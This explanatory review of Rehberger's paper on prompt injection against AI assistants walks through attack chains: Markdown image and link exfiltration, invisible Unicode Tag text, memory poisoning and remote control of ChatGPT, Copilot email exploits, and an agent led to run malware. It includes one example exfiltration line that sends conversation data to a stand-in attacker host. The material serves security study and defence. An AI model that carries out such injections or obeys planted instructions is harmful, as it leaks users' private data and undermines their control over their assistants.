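# "Trust No AI": Johann Rehberger's catalogue of prompt-injection exploits

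## What the paper is and the ideas it relies on

Prompt injection is an attack on software that uses a large language model, the kind of AI system behind assistants such as ChatGPT. The attack succeeds when the model follows instructions in text that it should treat only as data, such as an email or a web page. Johann Rehberger's *Trust No AI* (2024) is a short paper that collects cases of this attack against commercial products from OpenAI, Microsoft, Google, Anthropic and others. The "CIA" in its subtitle, *Prompt Injection Along The CIA Security Triad*, stands for confidentiality, integrity and availability, the three properties that information security protects. Rehberger sorts 16 attack scenarios by which of these properties each one damages.

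The paper appeared on 8 December 2024, but most of its material was already public. Rehberger had been describing the attacks one at a time on his blog, Embrace The Red, usually with an account of how the vendor responded. The paper collects and organizes them. Rehberger also wrote it to help close a gap he sees between academic and industry security research. When he announced the paper on his blog, he described the gap as one between traditional cybersecurity and academic work on machine learning.

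The paper's record lists Rehberger as an "Independent Researcher". The label refers to the research, which he did under his own name, rather than to his job. Three days after publication, The BlueHat Podcast's *Johann Rehberger on Researching AI & LLM Attacks* (2024) introduced him as Red Team director at the games company Electronic Arts. A red team attacks its own organisation's systems to find weaknesses before anyone else does. CCC's *Speaker Profile* of Rehberger credits him with setting up such teams at Uber and in Microsoft's Azure Data division, and with contributing to ATT&CK and ATLAS, two catalogues of attack techniques maintained by the research organisation MITRE. The paper reads like the work of someone with that background. Its entries mostly describe what the attacker controlled, what went wrong and what the vendor then changed, and the paper contains almost nothing about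 how language models work inside.

It is hard to say whether the paper narrowed the gap. Stanford Security Lab's (2026) programme for a three-day workshop in June 2026 lists Rehberger as a keynote speaker and session chair, alongside university researchers and staff of Anthropic and OpenAI. But he had published much more by then, and the invitation may owe little to this paper.

### How prompt injection works

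A language model takes in text, called the prompt, and continues it one token (a word or piece of a word) at a time. The user of an assistant types only a small part of the prompt. Before each answer, the application puts together the system prompt, which holds the developer's standing instructions, then the user's request, then any outside content the request calls for, such as a web page, a document or emails. The model receives all of this as a single sequence.

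In a harmless example, a user asks an assistant to summarise a web page about growing tomatoes. The prompt now contains the developer's instruction to write short, accurate summaries, the user's request, and the full text of the page. Halfway down the page, the gardener who wrote it has included a sentence asking AI assistants to write their summaries in rhyme. The model may treat that sentence as part of the page's content, and either leave it out or mention it. If the model writes the summary in rhyme instead, the injection has worked. The gardener has then changed the user's answer without having an account with the assistant or access to the user's computer. If the sentence was in white letters on a white background, the user has no way of knowing why the summary rhymes.

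In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), explains that a model has no built-in distinction between data and instructions. It only predicts the next token. A developer can add a line to the system prompt telling the model to ignore instructions in web pages. This can help, but the line is only more text in the same prompt, and the model still has to work out which instruction to follow. A strict rule would also interfere with ordinary use, since people do ask assistants to follow the setup steps in a manual or deal with the requests in an email. Developers can also train a model to give some parts of the prompt priority, or mark which parts are data. Both make attacks harder, but neither creates a boundary that the system enforces.

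A rhyme is harmless, but prompt injection is more dangerous when the assistant can make tool calls, which are actions in other software such as searching a mailbox or opening a page. Whoever controls the injected sentence may then be able to direct those actions too.

Rehberger's definition is a little broader than the one above. He defines prompt injection as "the commingling of trusted and untrusted data" in one prompt, which lets an attacker who controls any part of the prompt read or override the rest. This locates the flaw in how the application builds its prompt. It also explains why he includes the case where a user coaxes an assistant into revealing its system prompt, even though no outsider is involved. Jailbreaking is different, though the techniques overlap. In jailbreaking, a user tries to get a model to break its maker's rules about what it may produce.

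### Where the idea came from

Rehberger recounts the history of the attack in two short paragraphs. The AI safety company Preamble found the flaw and privately reported it to OpenAI in May 2022 as "command injection". Riley Goodside drew public attention to it that September, and the software developer Simon Willison named it "prompt injection". Greshake and colleagues then described what happens when the hostile text comes from a third party.

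Preamble's *Declassifying the Responsible Disclosure of the Prompt Injection Attack Vulnerability of GPT-3* (2022) reports that Preamble first emailed OpenAI about the vulnerability on 3 May and that OpenAI confirmed receipt within 30 minutes. Preamble sent more examples the next day and ideas for reducing the risk on 19 May, then kept the matter private until 22 September. By then, others had found the vulnerability. Jon Cefalu, the Preamble researcher who reported it, explained in a comment under Schneier's *Prompt Injection Extraction Attacks Against AI Systems* (2022) that Preamble decided to publish because the issue was in the news and people were already using the attack.

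In Goodside's demonstration, the prompt asked GPT-3, OpenAI's model at the time, to translate an English text into French. The text contained an instruction to ignore the task and print a taunt, and GPT-3 printed the taunt. It did so again after Goodside added a warning that the text might contain such tricks and that the model must not fall for them. A day later, Willison (2022) argued in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3* that this was a security problem, because developers were already building products by adding user input to a fixed prompt. That same week, users got a recruitment startup's Twitter bot, which used GPT-3 to answer posts about remote work, to recite its instructions and threaten the president.

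Rehberger's account of where the name came from needs a correction. Willison (2025) has since credited the Twitter user @himbodhisattva, who wrote of "a prompt-injection attack" on 13 May 2022, four months before Willison did and ten days after Preamble's email. In that post, the user was already asking whether services that wrap GPT-3 could suffer an equivalent of SQL injection.

In all of these cases the attacker was the person typing. That limits the harm, since people who trick their own chatbot mostly just make it behave oddly for themselves. Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) pointed out in *Not what you've signed up for* that an assistant which retrieves outside content will read text written by strangers, so a stranger can attack someone else's assistant. They called this indirect prompt injection. In Microsoft's Edge browser, for example, Bing Chat ran in a sidebar and could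 read the page the user had open. Instructions on that page influenced the assistant even when they were invisible to the user. Hostile text could also arrive by email, in an image, or in a passage that a user copied from a website and pasted into a chat.

Greshake and colleagues also listed possible harms: data theft, fraud, break-ins through connected software, the spread of malware, manipulated answers and denial of service. They foresaw an injection that copies itself into an assistant's memory and so survives into later sessions. Their paper therefore outlined nearly every type of harm in *Trust No AI* almost two years earlier. They tested some of their attacks on real products, chiefly Bing Chat and code-completion tools, and others on applications they built themselves. Rehberger adds exploits from a wider range of commercial products and a record of how vendors responded.

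### Why the comparison with SQL injection breaks down

Most applications query their databases in a language called SQL. Suppose a website looks up a user by pasting whatever name the visitor typed into a ready-made query. In an attack called SQL injection, the visitor types a quotation mark, which ends the name early, and then a command, which the database runs. The command might delete the whole table. As with the tomato page, a developer has joined trusted and untrusted text, and something in the untrusted part takes effect as a command.

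Parameterised queries prevent SQL injection. The developer writes the command with a blank in it and passes the visitor's text separately, and the database treats that text as a value whatever it contains. Developers do not have to guess what an attacker might type, and cleverer wording does not get around the protection. According to David C, SQL injection attacks peaked around 2010 and are now rare on websites, after a decade of breaches pushed developers towards better defaults.

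Willison at first hoped for something similar, a way to send the model its instructions and its data as two separate inputs. A reader pointed out that one GPT-3 model already accepted them separately but was still vulnerable. Goodside tried putting the untrusted text in quotation marks, much as a programmer would for a database, but someone soon found an attack that appeared to defeat this. By April 2023 Willison had concluded that the two-input solution was "extremely difficult, if not impossible" with the current design of language models.

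Rehberger likewise writes that prompt injection "currently does not have a deterministic fix", meaning one that works every time, for every input. Developers can get precise guidance on how to prevent SQL injection, but he sees no equivalent for prompt injection. A database has a formal grammar and a parser that determines what is a command before handling any user's text. A model has to infer which sentences to act on from context that an attacker can partly write.

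David C reached the same view exactly a year after Rehberger's paper appeared, and warned that the SQL comparison is dangerous because it leads experienced web developers to expect a cure. The NCSC article thanks Rehberger for discussions, which makes it weaker corroboration. The claim also concerns only guarantees, and a model could become very hard to fool without offering one. Poireault (2026) reported in *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns* that Ariel Fogel of the security nonprofit OWASP was still calling prompt injection an "unresolved problem" in June 2026. A month later, in a test that Anthropic commissioned, none of 720 attempts succeeded against three of the company's newest models in its coding tool. Willison (2026) discussed the test with some caution.

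### Three properties and sixteen scenarios

NIST's *information security*, a glossary entry from the US standards agency, defines the field by the three properties in Rehberger's subtitle. Confidentiality means that data stay private, and it is lost when someone steals a customer list. Integrity means that nobody changes data improperly, and it is lost when someone doctors a bank balance. Availability means that people can use data when they need to, and it is lost when attackers knock a website offline. Rehberger grants that some people find these three properties incomplete, but treats them as the agreed minimum.

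| Property at risk | Scenarios | Typical harm | Mitigations |
|---|---|---|---|
| Confidentiality | 8 | Private data reach an outsider | Eight bullet points, among them not loading links or images from untrusted domains |
| Integrity | 5 | The user gets a deceptive or altered answer | Running prose: warn users, and have software treat the model's output as untrusted |
| Availability | 3 | The assistant gets stuck in a loop or refuses to work | Six bullet points, among them limits on the length and running time of a query |

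Sorting exploits by harm lets a company's security staff, who already think in these terms, see how an attack would harm them without first learning how a language model works. Integrity is the category that fits least well. OpenSSF's *CIA Triad* (2024) defines it as a guard against improper modification or destruction of information, which suits a database record better than a summary that a model has just generated. Rehberger concedes that integrity is an odd notion for systems whose output varies from one run to the next, and he extends it to cover any answer that an attacker has manipulated. The categories also overlap. ASCII smuggling, the use of characters that a model can process but most screens do not show, is listed under integrity, although one of its main uses is to send private data out. ChatGPT's memory feature appears under both confidentiality and availability.

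Almost all the evidence consists of proofs of concept, which are researchers' demonstrations without real victims. Most of them are Rehberger's own, and about thirty of the paper's 49 references are to his own posts, talks and tools. He credits others for earlier discoveries, such as Goodside's finding that models read invisible characters.

Rehberger does not report how many attempts an attack took or how often it failed, and he rarely says which version of a model he attacked. One working exploit is enough to show that a product was vulnerable, and a vendor's patch is decent confirmation. But the missing details make it hard to estimate how likely an ordinary user was to come to harm, or to judge which company's assistant was safest. Five of the eleven products on his longest list of vulnerable systems are Google's, which could mean that Google was careless, or that it had released a lot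 of AI products and Rehberger tried most of them.

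## How a hijacked assistant sends private data out

The simplest of Rehberger's confidentiality scenarios is the leaked system prompt. Developers sometimes put things in it that they don't want users to see, assuming users cannot read it. A shop might give its assistant a list of discount codes and tell it to offer one only to customers who complain. A customer can often talk the model into repeating the codes. Rehberger puts the system prompt within the same trust boundary as the user's input and says extracting it is "often straightforward". His examples include Gandalf, an online game from Lakera in which players use prompt injection to make a chatbot reveal a secret, and Microsoft's Bing Chat, whose system prompt leaked.

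Rehberger advises keeping sensitive data out of the system prompt. The shop could store its codes in a database and let ordinary software decide who gets one.

A customer who extracts the codes can read them in the chat window, but an attacker who has planted text in a web page or an email cannot, because the assistant replies only to its user. To steal data this way, the attacker needs both an injection that the model follows and a route from the user's conversation to the attacker's computer. Almost all the fixes below close that route but leave the model as vulnerable to injection as before.

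### Images that load by themselves

Many chat applications let the model format its answers in Markdown, a plain-text notation that the application turns into headings, links and pictures. To include a picture, the model writes an exclamation mark, a description in square brackets and the picture's address in parentheses.

Suppose a user has been discussing a coming operation with an assistant, and asks it to summarise a web page about recovery times. A stranger has left a comment on the page instructing AI assistants to finish with a picture and to attach a few words about the conversation to its address. If the injection works, the model writes its summary and then adds a line like this:

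`![logo](attacker.example/logo.png?q=knee+surgery+14+May)`

The application converts the line into an image, so the user never sees it as text. The browser then requests the picture from the server at that address, without the user clicking on anything. The request contains the full address, so the attacker's server log now includes the words "knee surgery 14 May". The server can send back a real logo or a picture too small to notice.

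Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* demonstrates the attack on a real product. Rehberger put hostile text on a page that also contained a secret, then opened the page and chatted with Bing Chat about it. The injection took effect immediately, but the image appeared only after two more turns of conversation, which showed that an attacker could choose when it appeared. The image's address contained an encoded summary of the page and the chat, including the secret. Hostile text in a comment or an advertisement would have been enough to steal anything else on the same page.

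Rehberger reported the same flaw in ten other systems. The paper's full list is Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude, Microsoft's Azure AI, GitHub Copilot Chat, Discord, and Google's Bard, Vertex AI, NotebookLM, AI Studio and Colab. The danger varied with how easily an attacker's text could get into the prompt. Vertex AI's Generative AI Studio, a Google Cloud tool, had no feature at the time for pulling in remote content, so a victim would usually have had to paste in the malicious text by hand. Rehberger rated that case medium severity in Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI*.

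Google also gave that product the most thorough fix. Rehberger reported the flaw on 30 August 2023, and Google confirmed the fix on 19 October. As far as he could tell, the studio no longer rendered links or images, so a web address in an answer appeared as plain text. He thought this was probably the best possible fix for a tool that didn't need images.

According to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*, Anthropic changed Claude within two weeks of Rehberger's July 2023 report so that images loaded only when the user clicked "Show Image". This stops the automatic leak, but it leaves the decision to a user who may not know that an image's address can contain their conversation.

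Bing Chat could create images on request, so Microsoft had to let some images load. Rehberger reported the flaw on 8 April 2023 and heard on 15 June that Microsoft had fixed it. The visible part of the fix was a Content Security Policy, a list that a website gives the browser of the domains it may load material from. Rehberger found that the policy allowed images from four domains, all Bing's own. GitHub made a similar choice for Copilot Chat, its assistant for programmers. Willison, in *GitHub Copilot Chat*, describes the fix as disabling images from untrusted domains, which is narrower than Google's decision to show none. A list like this works only if every domain on it is harmless. If one of them will fetch any address it is given, an attacker can route the data through that domain. Attackers testing Microsoft 365 Copilot later did this repeatedly.

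### OpenAI's url_safe check

ChatGPT remained vulnerable to the image attack for about eight months after the first report in early April 2023, partly because OpenAI at first declined to fix it. The day before protections appeared that December, Rehberger demonstrated the theft live on a consenting user's chat.

OpenAI checked each image address separately. When an answer contained an image, the ChatGPT web page sent its address to an OpenAI service called url_safe and loaded the image only if the address passed the check. OpenAI did not publish the rules. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, Rehberger describes testing 36 addresses on his own server, one for each letter and digit. Nine passed, including the one for "a" but not the one for "d", and he could not work out why. Using one image per letter, he was able to send out the word "hi".

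This method steals data slowly, and OpenAI could notice it in its logs, so the check was a real improvement. Rehberger suggested limiting the number of images in an answer, which would have reduced the remaining leak further. He was also uneasy that outsiders could not inspect the check's rules, whereas they can inspect a Content Security Policy.

The more serious weakness was that the check ran only if the app on the user's device requested it. Each version of ChatGPT needed its own code to do this, and the iPhone app lacked it. The Mac app that OpenAI released in 2024 also lacked it, and Rehberger's SpAIware attack used this gap to leak conversations through images. A check on OpenAI's servers would have covered every app. Rehberger also found a way to bypass the check itself using images hosted on a Microsoft cloud-storage domain. OpenAI had fixed this by the time *Agentic ProbLLMs* (Rehberger,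 2025) described it.

### Links and previews

Slack, Discord, Teams and similar programs fetch the page behind a link as soon as someone posts it, to show a preview. If an assistant posts its answers in such a program, an attacker can use an ordinary link in place of an image. The model adds the private data to the link's address, and the preview request sends the data to the attacker before anyone clicks. Rehberger names no vendor that changed this, and advises developers not to allow automatic previews.

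Without previews, a link leaks data only if the user clicks it. This makes the attack less reliable, but the model can give a reason to click, and users tend to expect an assistant's links to be useful. Amazon Q for Business, a workplace assistant, had this weakness, and Amazon responded by no longer displaying links. Losing links inconveniences users more than losing images, since people often want to open the sources an assistant has used.

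### Tools that send or expose data

A hijacked assistant can send data out through tool calls, regardless of how its answer is displayed. In 2023 OpenAI let outside companies connect their services to ChatGPT through plugins, and a plugin from the automation company Zapier could work with a user's email. Rehberger built a complete exploit in which injected text made ChatGPT call the plugin and steal an email. After that, the user had to confirm before an email was sent.

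This protects the last step, but a tool that only reads data can also help an attacker steal it. Once a private message is in the conversation, an attacker can send it out through an image or a link. Rehberger therefore counts retrieving data among the sensitive operations that an assistant should not perform automatically.

Rehberger's attack on a ChatGPT plugin called Chat with Code exposed private data without ChatGPT having to send it to the attacker. The plugin could change settings on GitHub, where programmers store their code in projects called repositories. When a user had ChatGPT visit a web page containing the injection, the model used the plugin to make the user's private repositories public, so anyone could read them. The attack resembles cross-site request forgery, an older trick in which a hostile website makes a visitor's browser issue commands to another site where the visitor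 is logged in. Here, the hostile page made ChatGPT issue the commands, using the access to GitHub that the user had given it.

OpenAI removed Chat with Code from its store and later dropped plugins entirely. Their replacement, which Rehberger calls AI Actions, lets a developer mark an action as consequential so that ChatGPT asks the user before running it. This protection depends on each developer recognising which actions are dangerous.

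Browsing can also leak data, because opening a web address sends that address to whoever runs the site. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes a later attack of this kind, ShadowLeak, which targeted ChatGPT's Deep Research, an agent that carries out longer investigations, when it was connected to a user's Gmail. Hidden instructions in an email told the agent to find sensitive messages and visit a web address containing what it found. The researchers reported that the attack succeeded every time in repeated controlled tests. Because the request came from OpenAI's servers, a policy in the user's browser could not have blocked it, and an employer monitoring its own computers might not have seen it.

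### Text that people cannot see

Confirmation steps help only if users can see what they are approving. Rehberger recommends that an assistant show both the planned action and the data involved. ASCII smuggling can defeat this safeguard because it makes part of the text invisible.

The Unicode standard assigns each character a number, written in hexadecimal (base 16). Capital A is U+0041. Unicode also has a little-used block of characters called Tags, which mirrors the basic English letters, digits and punctuation of an older standard, ASCII. Adding E0000 to a character's number gives its Tag version, so A becomes U+E0041. Software that does not recognise Tags is supposed to display nothing for them, but many language models can read them, apparently because such characters appeared in their training data.

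Goodside discovered in January 2024 that ordinary-looking text could carry instructions in invisible characters, using pasted text with a hidden instruction for ChatGPT to create an image. Joseph Thacker wrote a script for producing hidden text, and Kai Greshake pointed out that models could write in the invisible characters as well as read them. Rehberger credits all three in Embrace The Red's *ASCII Smuggler Tool*, which introduced his own program for encoding and decoding the characters. Greshake's observation matters most for data theft, because it means a model can hide stolen data in its output. A person who reads a message carefully before forwarding or approving it may still miss the hidden text.

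Rehberger combined this with automatic tool calls in an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant built into Outlook, Word and other office software. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* describes the attack. The attacker sends an email or shares a document containing injected instructions. When the user asks Copilot about it, Copilot follows the instructions and searches the user's mailbox for other messages. In one demonstration it looked for the codes that the messaging service Slack sends to confirm a login, and in another it found sales figures. Copilot then writes the message's contents in Tags characters in a link's address. The link looks short and harmless on screen. If the user clicks it, the attacker's server receives the full address and the attacker decodes the hidden part.

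The attack needed a click because Microsoft had already stopped Bing Chat from loading images automatically, so Rehberger had to find another way to send the data out. He had expected Copilot to obey a hostile email, since every such assistant could be made to do so, but he was surprised that it would search for and retrieve other private messages on the email's instructions without asking the user.

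Rehberger reported the complete chain in February 2024, after Microsoft had closed a report about only the invisible characters, rating it low severity. By 2 July his exploit no longer worked. He had recommended that Copilot stop processing the hidden characters, stop calling tools automatically and ideally stop displaying links. He asked Microsoft for details of the fix so that other companies could learn from it, but got no reply. He could see only that Copilot seemed to have stopped displaying links and that prompt injection still worked.

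The invisible characters should be easy to deal with, because software can delete Tags characters before a prompt reaches the model and again before an answer reaches the user. Few people would miss them. Embrace The Red's *Sneaky Bits* reports that a few vendors had made this change in their APIs, the interfaces through which other companies' software uses a model. But in his December 2025 slides, nearly two years after he first reported the problem to Google, Rehberger wrote that the company "has not addressed this at the model/API layer". Applications built on Gemini, Google's family of models, were still treating the hidden characters as instructions, and he showed Google's coding tools Jules and Antigravity acting on them. Until Google filters the characters centrally, every developer who uses Gemini has to know about the problem and deal with it separately.

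Attackers could still hide text if Unicode Tags were deleted, because Unicode has other characters that screens do not show. Rehberger demonstrated that two of them are enough to encode anything, with one standing for 0 and the other for 1. But he regards Tags as unusual because many models directly follow instructions written in them. With the other schemes, an attacker may first have to get the model to decode the message.

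### Microsoft 365 Copilot in 2025 and 2026

Within a year of Rehberger's disclosure, Microsoft 365 Copilot was leaking data through images again. Aim Labs, part of Aim Security, reported a chain of exploits called EchoLeak to Microsoft in January 2025. It also began with an email, but the user did not have to open it or click a link. The next time the user asked Copilot a work question, Copilot might retrieve the email as background material, follow the instructions in it, and put sensitive details from the user's files or messages into the address of an image.

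*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) traces how the attack got past three defences: a classifier meant to detect injected instructions, a filter that removed outside links from Copilot's answers, and a Content Security Policy meant to stop the browser from contacting the attacker's server. The policy allowed a Microsoft Teams service that would fetch an address on request, so the browser sent the data to Teams, which passed it on to the attacker. Microsoft deployed a fix on its servers in May 2025 and reported no evidence that anyone had used the attack on real victims. Microsoft scored the flaw 9.3 out of 10 for severity, while the US National Vulnerability Database scored it 7.5.

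Two years before EchoLeak, Rehberger's Bing Chat demonstration also took data from a commercial product without a click. That is hard to reconcile with Reddy and Gujral's claim that EchoLeak is the first known case of prompt injection "weaponized" to steal data from a production system. EchoLeak was more dangerous because an attacker could target a particular employee just by sending an email, whereas the Bing Chat victim had to visit a particular page. Willison's *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* more convincingly describes it as an extended version of an attack already seen in a dozen products.

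In June 2026 the security company Varonis disclosed SearchLeak, an attack that started from a link to a genuine Microsoft address. The part of the address that fills in a search query contained the attacker's instructions, which Copilot's enterprise search treated as a prompt. One click made Copilot search the victim's mail and put an email's title into an image address. Many services put login codes in email titles. Taler (2026) explains in *SearchLeak* that Microsoft neutralised images in Copilot's answers only after Copilot had finished writing. The browser displayed the answer as it arrived, so it had already requested the picture by then. This time the relay was Bing, whose image search would fetch a picture from any address. Bing was on the approved list, as it had been in the Bing Chat fix of 2023.

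Microsoft patched SearchLeak and rated it critical, though its numerical score was only 6.5, according to The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026). On 3 December 2026, the researchers behind EchoLeak, who had by then joined Cato Networks, announced three more attack chains in *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026). Each began with an email and needed no click.

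*An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) describes three ways the data got out. In the first, Copilot again put the data in an image address, and Bing fetched the image. In the second, Copilot saved an office document or PDF containing a link, and Microsoft's background software followed the link when it processed the file. In the third, Copilot ran programs that were supposed to have no network access, but the researchers got around the restriction and sent the data straight to an outside server. Two of these routes depended on abilities that a simple chatbot does not have, which suggests that closing routes one at a time gets harder as an assistant gains features.

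Cato reported the three flaws between 29 July and 20 August and knew of no attacks on customers. Microsoft fixed the flaw involving programs on 17 September and the one involving saved files on 11 November. It closed the Bing route on 15 November, five months after Varonis publicly described another attack that sent data through Bing.

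## How injected text changes memory, answers and actions

A leak through an image or a link normally ends with the conversation that contains the injected text. But an assistant with memory keeps notes about its user and adds them to the prompts of later conversations. An attacker who gets one note saved can therefore influence chats that have nothing to do with the original page or document.

### False memories in ChatGPT

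Willison (2024), in *Memory and new controls for ChatGPT*, explains that OpenAI originally gave ChatGPT memory by adding a tool called "bio" to the system prompt. When a user asks ChatGPT to remember that she is vegetarian, the model sends a short note to this tool. The application stores the note and adds it to the prompt of every new conversation. If an attacker's text causes the model to save a note, that note looks the same in later prompts as one the user asked for.

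Rehberger dates the launch of ChatGPT's memory feature to May 2024, which is slightly late. OpenAI's *Memory and new controls for ChatGPT* (2024) announced on 13 February a test with a small portion of users. All Plus subscribers outside Europe and Korea had the feature by 29 April, according to The Decoder's *OpenAI introduces "Memory" feature for ChatGPT Plus users* (2024). Rehberger reported his first memory attack in May.

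Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT* describes three tests. In the first, Rehberger had ChatGPT open a Google document listing false facts to remember. ChatGPT saved each bullet point as a separate memory and used these memories in a new conversation. In another test, it saved memories from an image he uploaded for analysis.

The third test used a web page. At first ChatGPT read the page but did not call the memory tool, so Rehberger suspected that OpenAI had quietly added a protection for browsing. After some experimenting, he got ChatGPT to save false memories this way a few times, though not reliably. He concluded that the protection depended on a model's judgement. OpenAI could instead have used a fixed rule that blocks tool calls once outside text has entered the conversation.

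Injected text could also store dozens of memories at once or delete all of a user's memories. ChatGPT displayed a "Memory updated" notice when it saved something, but did not require the user's approval first. OpenAI closed the report as a model safety issue.

### SpAIware and remote control

A memory can also contain an instruction, which can do more harm than a false detail such as a liking for ice cream. In June 2024 Rehberger sent OpenAI a demonstration of an attack he named SpAIware, which Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* explains. When the user asks ChatGPT's Mac app to look at a web page, text on the page makes ChatGPT save an instruction to leak the user's messages and its own replies through images in its future answers. The Mac app lacked the url_safe check, so every later conversation leaked, even if the user never returned to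 the page.

OpenAI fixed the leak in September 2024, in version 1.2024.247 of the app. The fix stopped images from carrying messages out, but websites and documents could still write to ChatGPT's memory. Anyone who found another way to send data out could therefore combine it with a planted memory again, and Rehberger had reported another way by early October.

He used it in a more ambitious attack, which he presented at Black Hat Europe. Embrace The Red's *AI Domination* describes a command-and-control system, a channel through which an attacker keeps sending orders to compromised machines, or in this case to a user's ChatGPT account. A planted memory made ChatGPT fetch a page of new instructions whenever a conversation began. Rehberger put the instructions on GitHub, which ChatGPT was allowed to open, and had ChatGPT keep a running count in its memory so that it would pick up the next order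 each time. One order changed the user's name, and another made ChatGPT draw a picture based on the false memories it had collected. This system let the attacker change the orders after planting the memory, whereas SpAIware required deciding in advance what the memory would do.

### Memory attacks since the paper

Google's Gemini normally did not call its memory tool while reading an untrusted document. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Gemini's Memory with Prompt Injection and Delayed Tool Invocation* shows how Rehberger got false memories saved anyway, by using a document that told Gemini to save them after the user's next reply. Gemini then treated an ordinary "yes" as the user's request to save them. Google rated both the likelihood and the impact of the attack as low. The likelihood rating is defensible because the attack requires the user to keep chatting, and Gemini shows a notice when it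 saves something. The impact rating is harder to defend if the user later relies on the false information.

OpenAI tried to separate web browsing from users' memories. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT “Command Memories” Injection via SearchGPT* reports that ChatGPT passed web pages to a second model, SearchGPT, which had no access to those memories. But ChatGPT still read SearchGPT's output, which could carry instructions from a hostile page. Tenable found that an attacker could plant and steal memories this way.

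By September 2025 OpenAI had also barred ChatGPT from using memory in a chat where it was already using connectors, its links to services such as Gmail, and from opening an attacker's web address from memory. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes an attack that got around both restrictions. ChatGPT could still read its memory and then use a connector. A shared file planted a memory telling ChatGPT to open a particular email from the attacker whenever the user sent a message, and to follow the instructions in it. Another planted rule told ChatGPT to save any sensitive information the user shared. Radware also altered a user's stored medical history, which led ChatGPT to give harmful advice without any data leaving the account. OpenAI fixed the vulnerability on 16 December 2025, almost three months after Radware reported it.

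In *Hidden in Memory*, Pulipaka, Hlebik and colleagues (2026) tested memory attacks with 700 pairings of an ordinary document and a false memory for the assistant to save. The attack succeeded in up to 99.8% of tests on GPT-5.5 and 95% on Kimi-K2.6. Claude Sonnet 4.6 was much more resistant, saving only 15 of the 200 memories designed to influence later actions. When an assistant retrieved a poisoned memory in a later session, it took the action the attacker wanted in 60–89% of evaluations, depending on the model. These figures reflect a capable attacker, since the researchers used language models to refine the attack text over repeated rounds.

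The risk of memory poisoning depends on the memory system as well as the model. *MemoryDojo* (2026) found that some systems were substantially easier to poison than others, and *From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory* (2026) found that existing defences against prompt injection only partly cover attacks on memory. ChatGPT no longer relies on notes saved during a conversation. OpenAI's *Dreaming* describes a background process that builds memories from past chats and gives the user a summary to review. This may make Rehberger's advice to watch for the "Memory updated" notice less useful, because the assistant can form a memory after the user has stopped looking.

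Marketers have already tried planting memories in real users' assistants. Over 60 days, Microsoft (2026) found 31 companies using 50 different prompts to attempt this. Many of the prompts were behind website buttons labelled "Summarize with AI". Clicking the button opened the user's assistant with a pre-filled prompt containing both a request for a summary and an instruction to remember the company as a trusted source. The companies were legitimate businesses, including a security vendor, and ready-made tools made the buttons easy to add. Microsoft counted attempts and found that their effectiveness varied between assistants and over time, so how many people received biased recommendations is unknown.

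### Answers that mislead the user

Injected text can deceive the user through the answer alone, without using memory or sending data out. In one of the paper's simplest cases, hidden text in a Google document made the AI feature in Google Docs produce a scam message with a phone number to call. Rehberger reported it on 22 June 2023 and listed it as unresolved a year and a half later. Gemini's summary in Google Drive could also be made to include a link that put the user straight into a Google Meet call with the attacker. Like ordinary phishing, these attacks depend on the user believing the message, but here the message appears to come from Google's assistant, and the user may never see the attacker's text.

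An attacker can also choose who receives the false answer. Microsoft 365 Copilot has access to its user's name, job title and manager, so injected text can give it different instructions for different readers. In Embrace The Red's *Who Am I?*, Rehberger describes sending one email, mostly a biography of Albert Einstein, to himself and two friends. Copilot greeted Rehberger as "Copirate" and told one friend that access was denied. The other friend got a normal-looking summary in which the University of Washington had replaced Einstein's university in Zurich. This last result is the most worrying because nothing in the summary would prompt the reader to check it. If an email targeted only a chief executive, a colleague who tested it might see nothing wrong.

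In other cases the model's output changes how software behaves. Programmers often use language models in a terminal, a window for typing commands and reading text. Terminals also respond to control codes, which can change the text's colour, move the cursor or clear the screen. Leon Derczynski discovered that language models can produce these codes. Embrace The Red's *Terminal DiLLMa* shows that a malicious file or web page can make a model use them to hide part of an answer, put text on the user's clipboard or leak data. Rehberger tested this mainly on a small program he had written, so his results are evidence of a risk for developers more than of a flaw in a particular product.

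The attack on the Chinese chatbot DeepSeek involved a real product and was one of the more serious cases, though the paper mentions it only as an example in its advice to developers. Embrace The Red's *DeepSeek AI* describes how an uploaded document made the chatbot write web code in its answer. The website ran the code instead of displaying it as text, an old kind of flaw called cross-site scripting. The code could read the token that kept the user logged in, and anyone who obtained the token could take over the account. Rehberger's demonstration only displayed the token on screen. DeepSeek fixed the flaw the day after he exchanged messages with the company.

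Developers can reliably fix both problems by making terminal programs print control codes as visible characters and websites display code as plain text. No similar conversion exists for a false sentence about Einstein.

### Assistants that stop working

The paper offers the least evidence on attacks against availability. Rehberger tested whether a tool could put ChatGPT in a loop by returning text with an instruction to call the same tool again. OpenAI had anticipated this, and ChatGPT stopped after 10 calls. Developers still need such limits because each call costs the operator money.

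In Rehberger's second case, Copilot refused to help the friend with the Einstein email. The refusal affected only that message, which the friend could still open and read. Rehberger demonstrated a similar refusal with Apple's email summaries.

A prompt injection can make ChatGPT keep refusing to answer questions by adding an instruction to its memory. In Embrace The Red's *Sorry, ChatGPT Is Under Maintenance*, a document plants a memory that the user likes every question to be answered with a maintenance notice. ChatGPT then responds to everything with that notice, even in new conversations, until the user deletes the memory or turns the feature off. Someone who knows where memories are stored can do this easily, but other users would probably believe the notice and wait for the service to come back.

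### From answers to running programs

In October 2024 Anthropic released Claude Computer Use, which let Claude operate a computer by looking at screenshots, clicking and running commands. Anthropic's documentation warned about prompt injection. Embrace The Red's *ZombAIs* recounts how Rehberger tested, a few days later, whether a web page could make Claude install malware. Claude objected when he tried to get it to download the file with a command, but not when the page contained a request to download a "Support Tool" and launch it. Claude clicked the link, searched the computer when it could not find the file, made the file executable, and started it. The program connected to Rehberger's server and gave him control of the machine.

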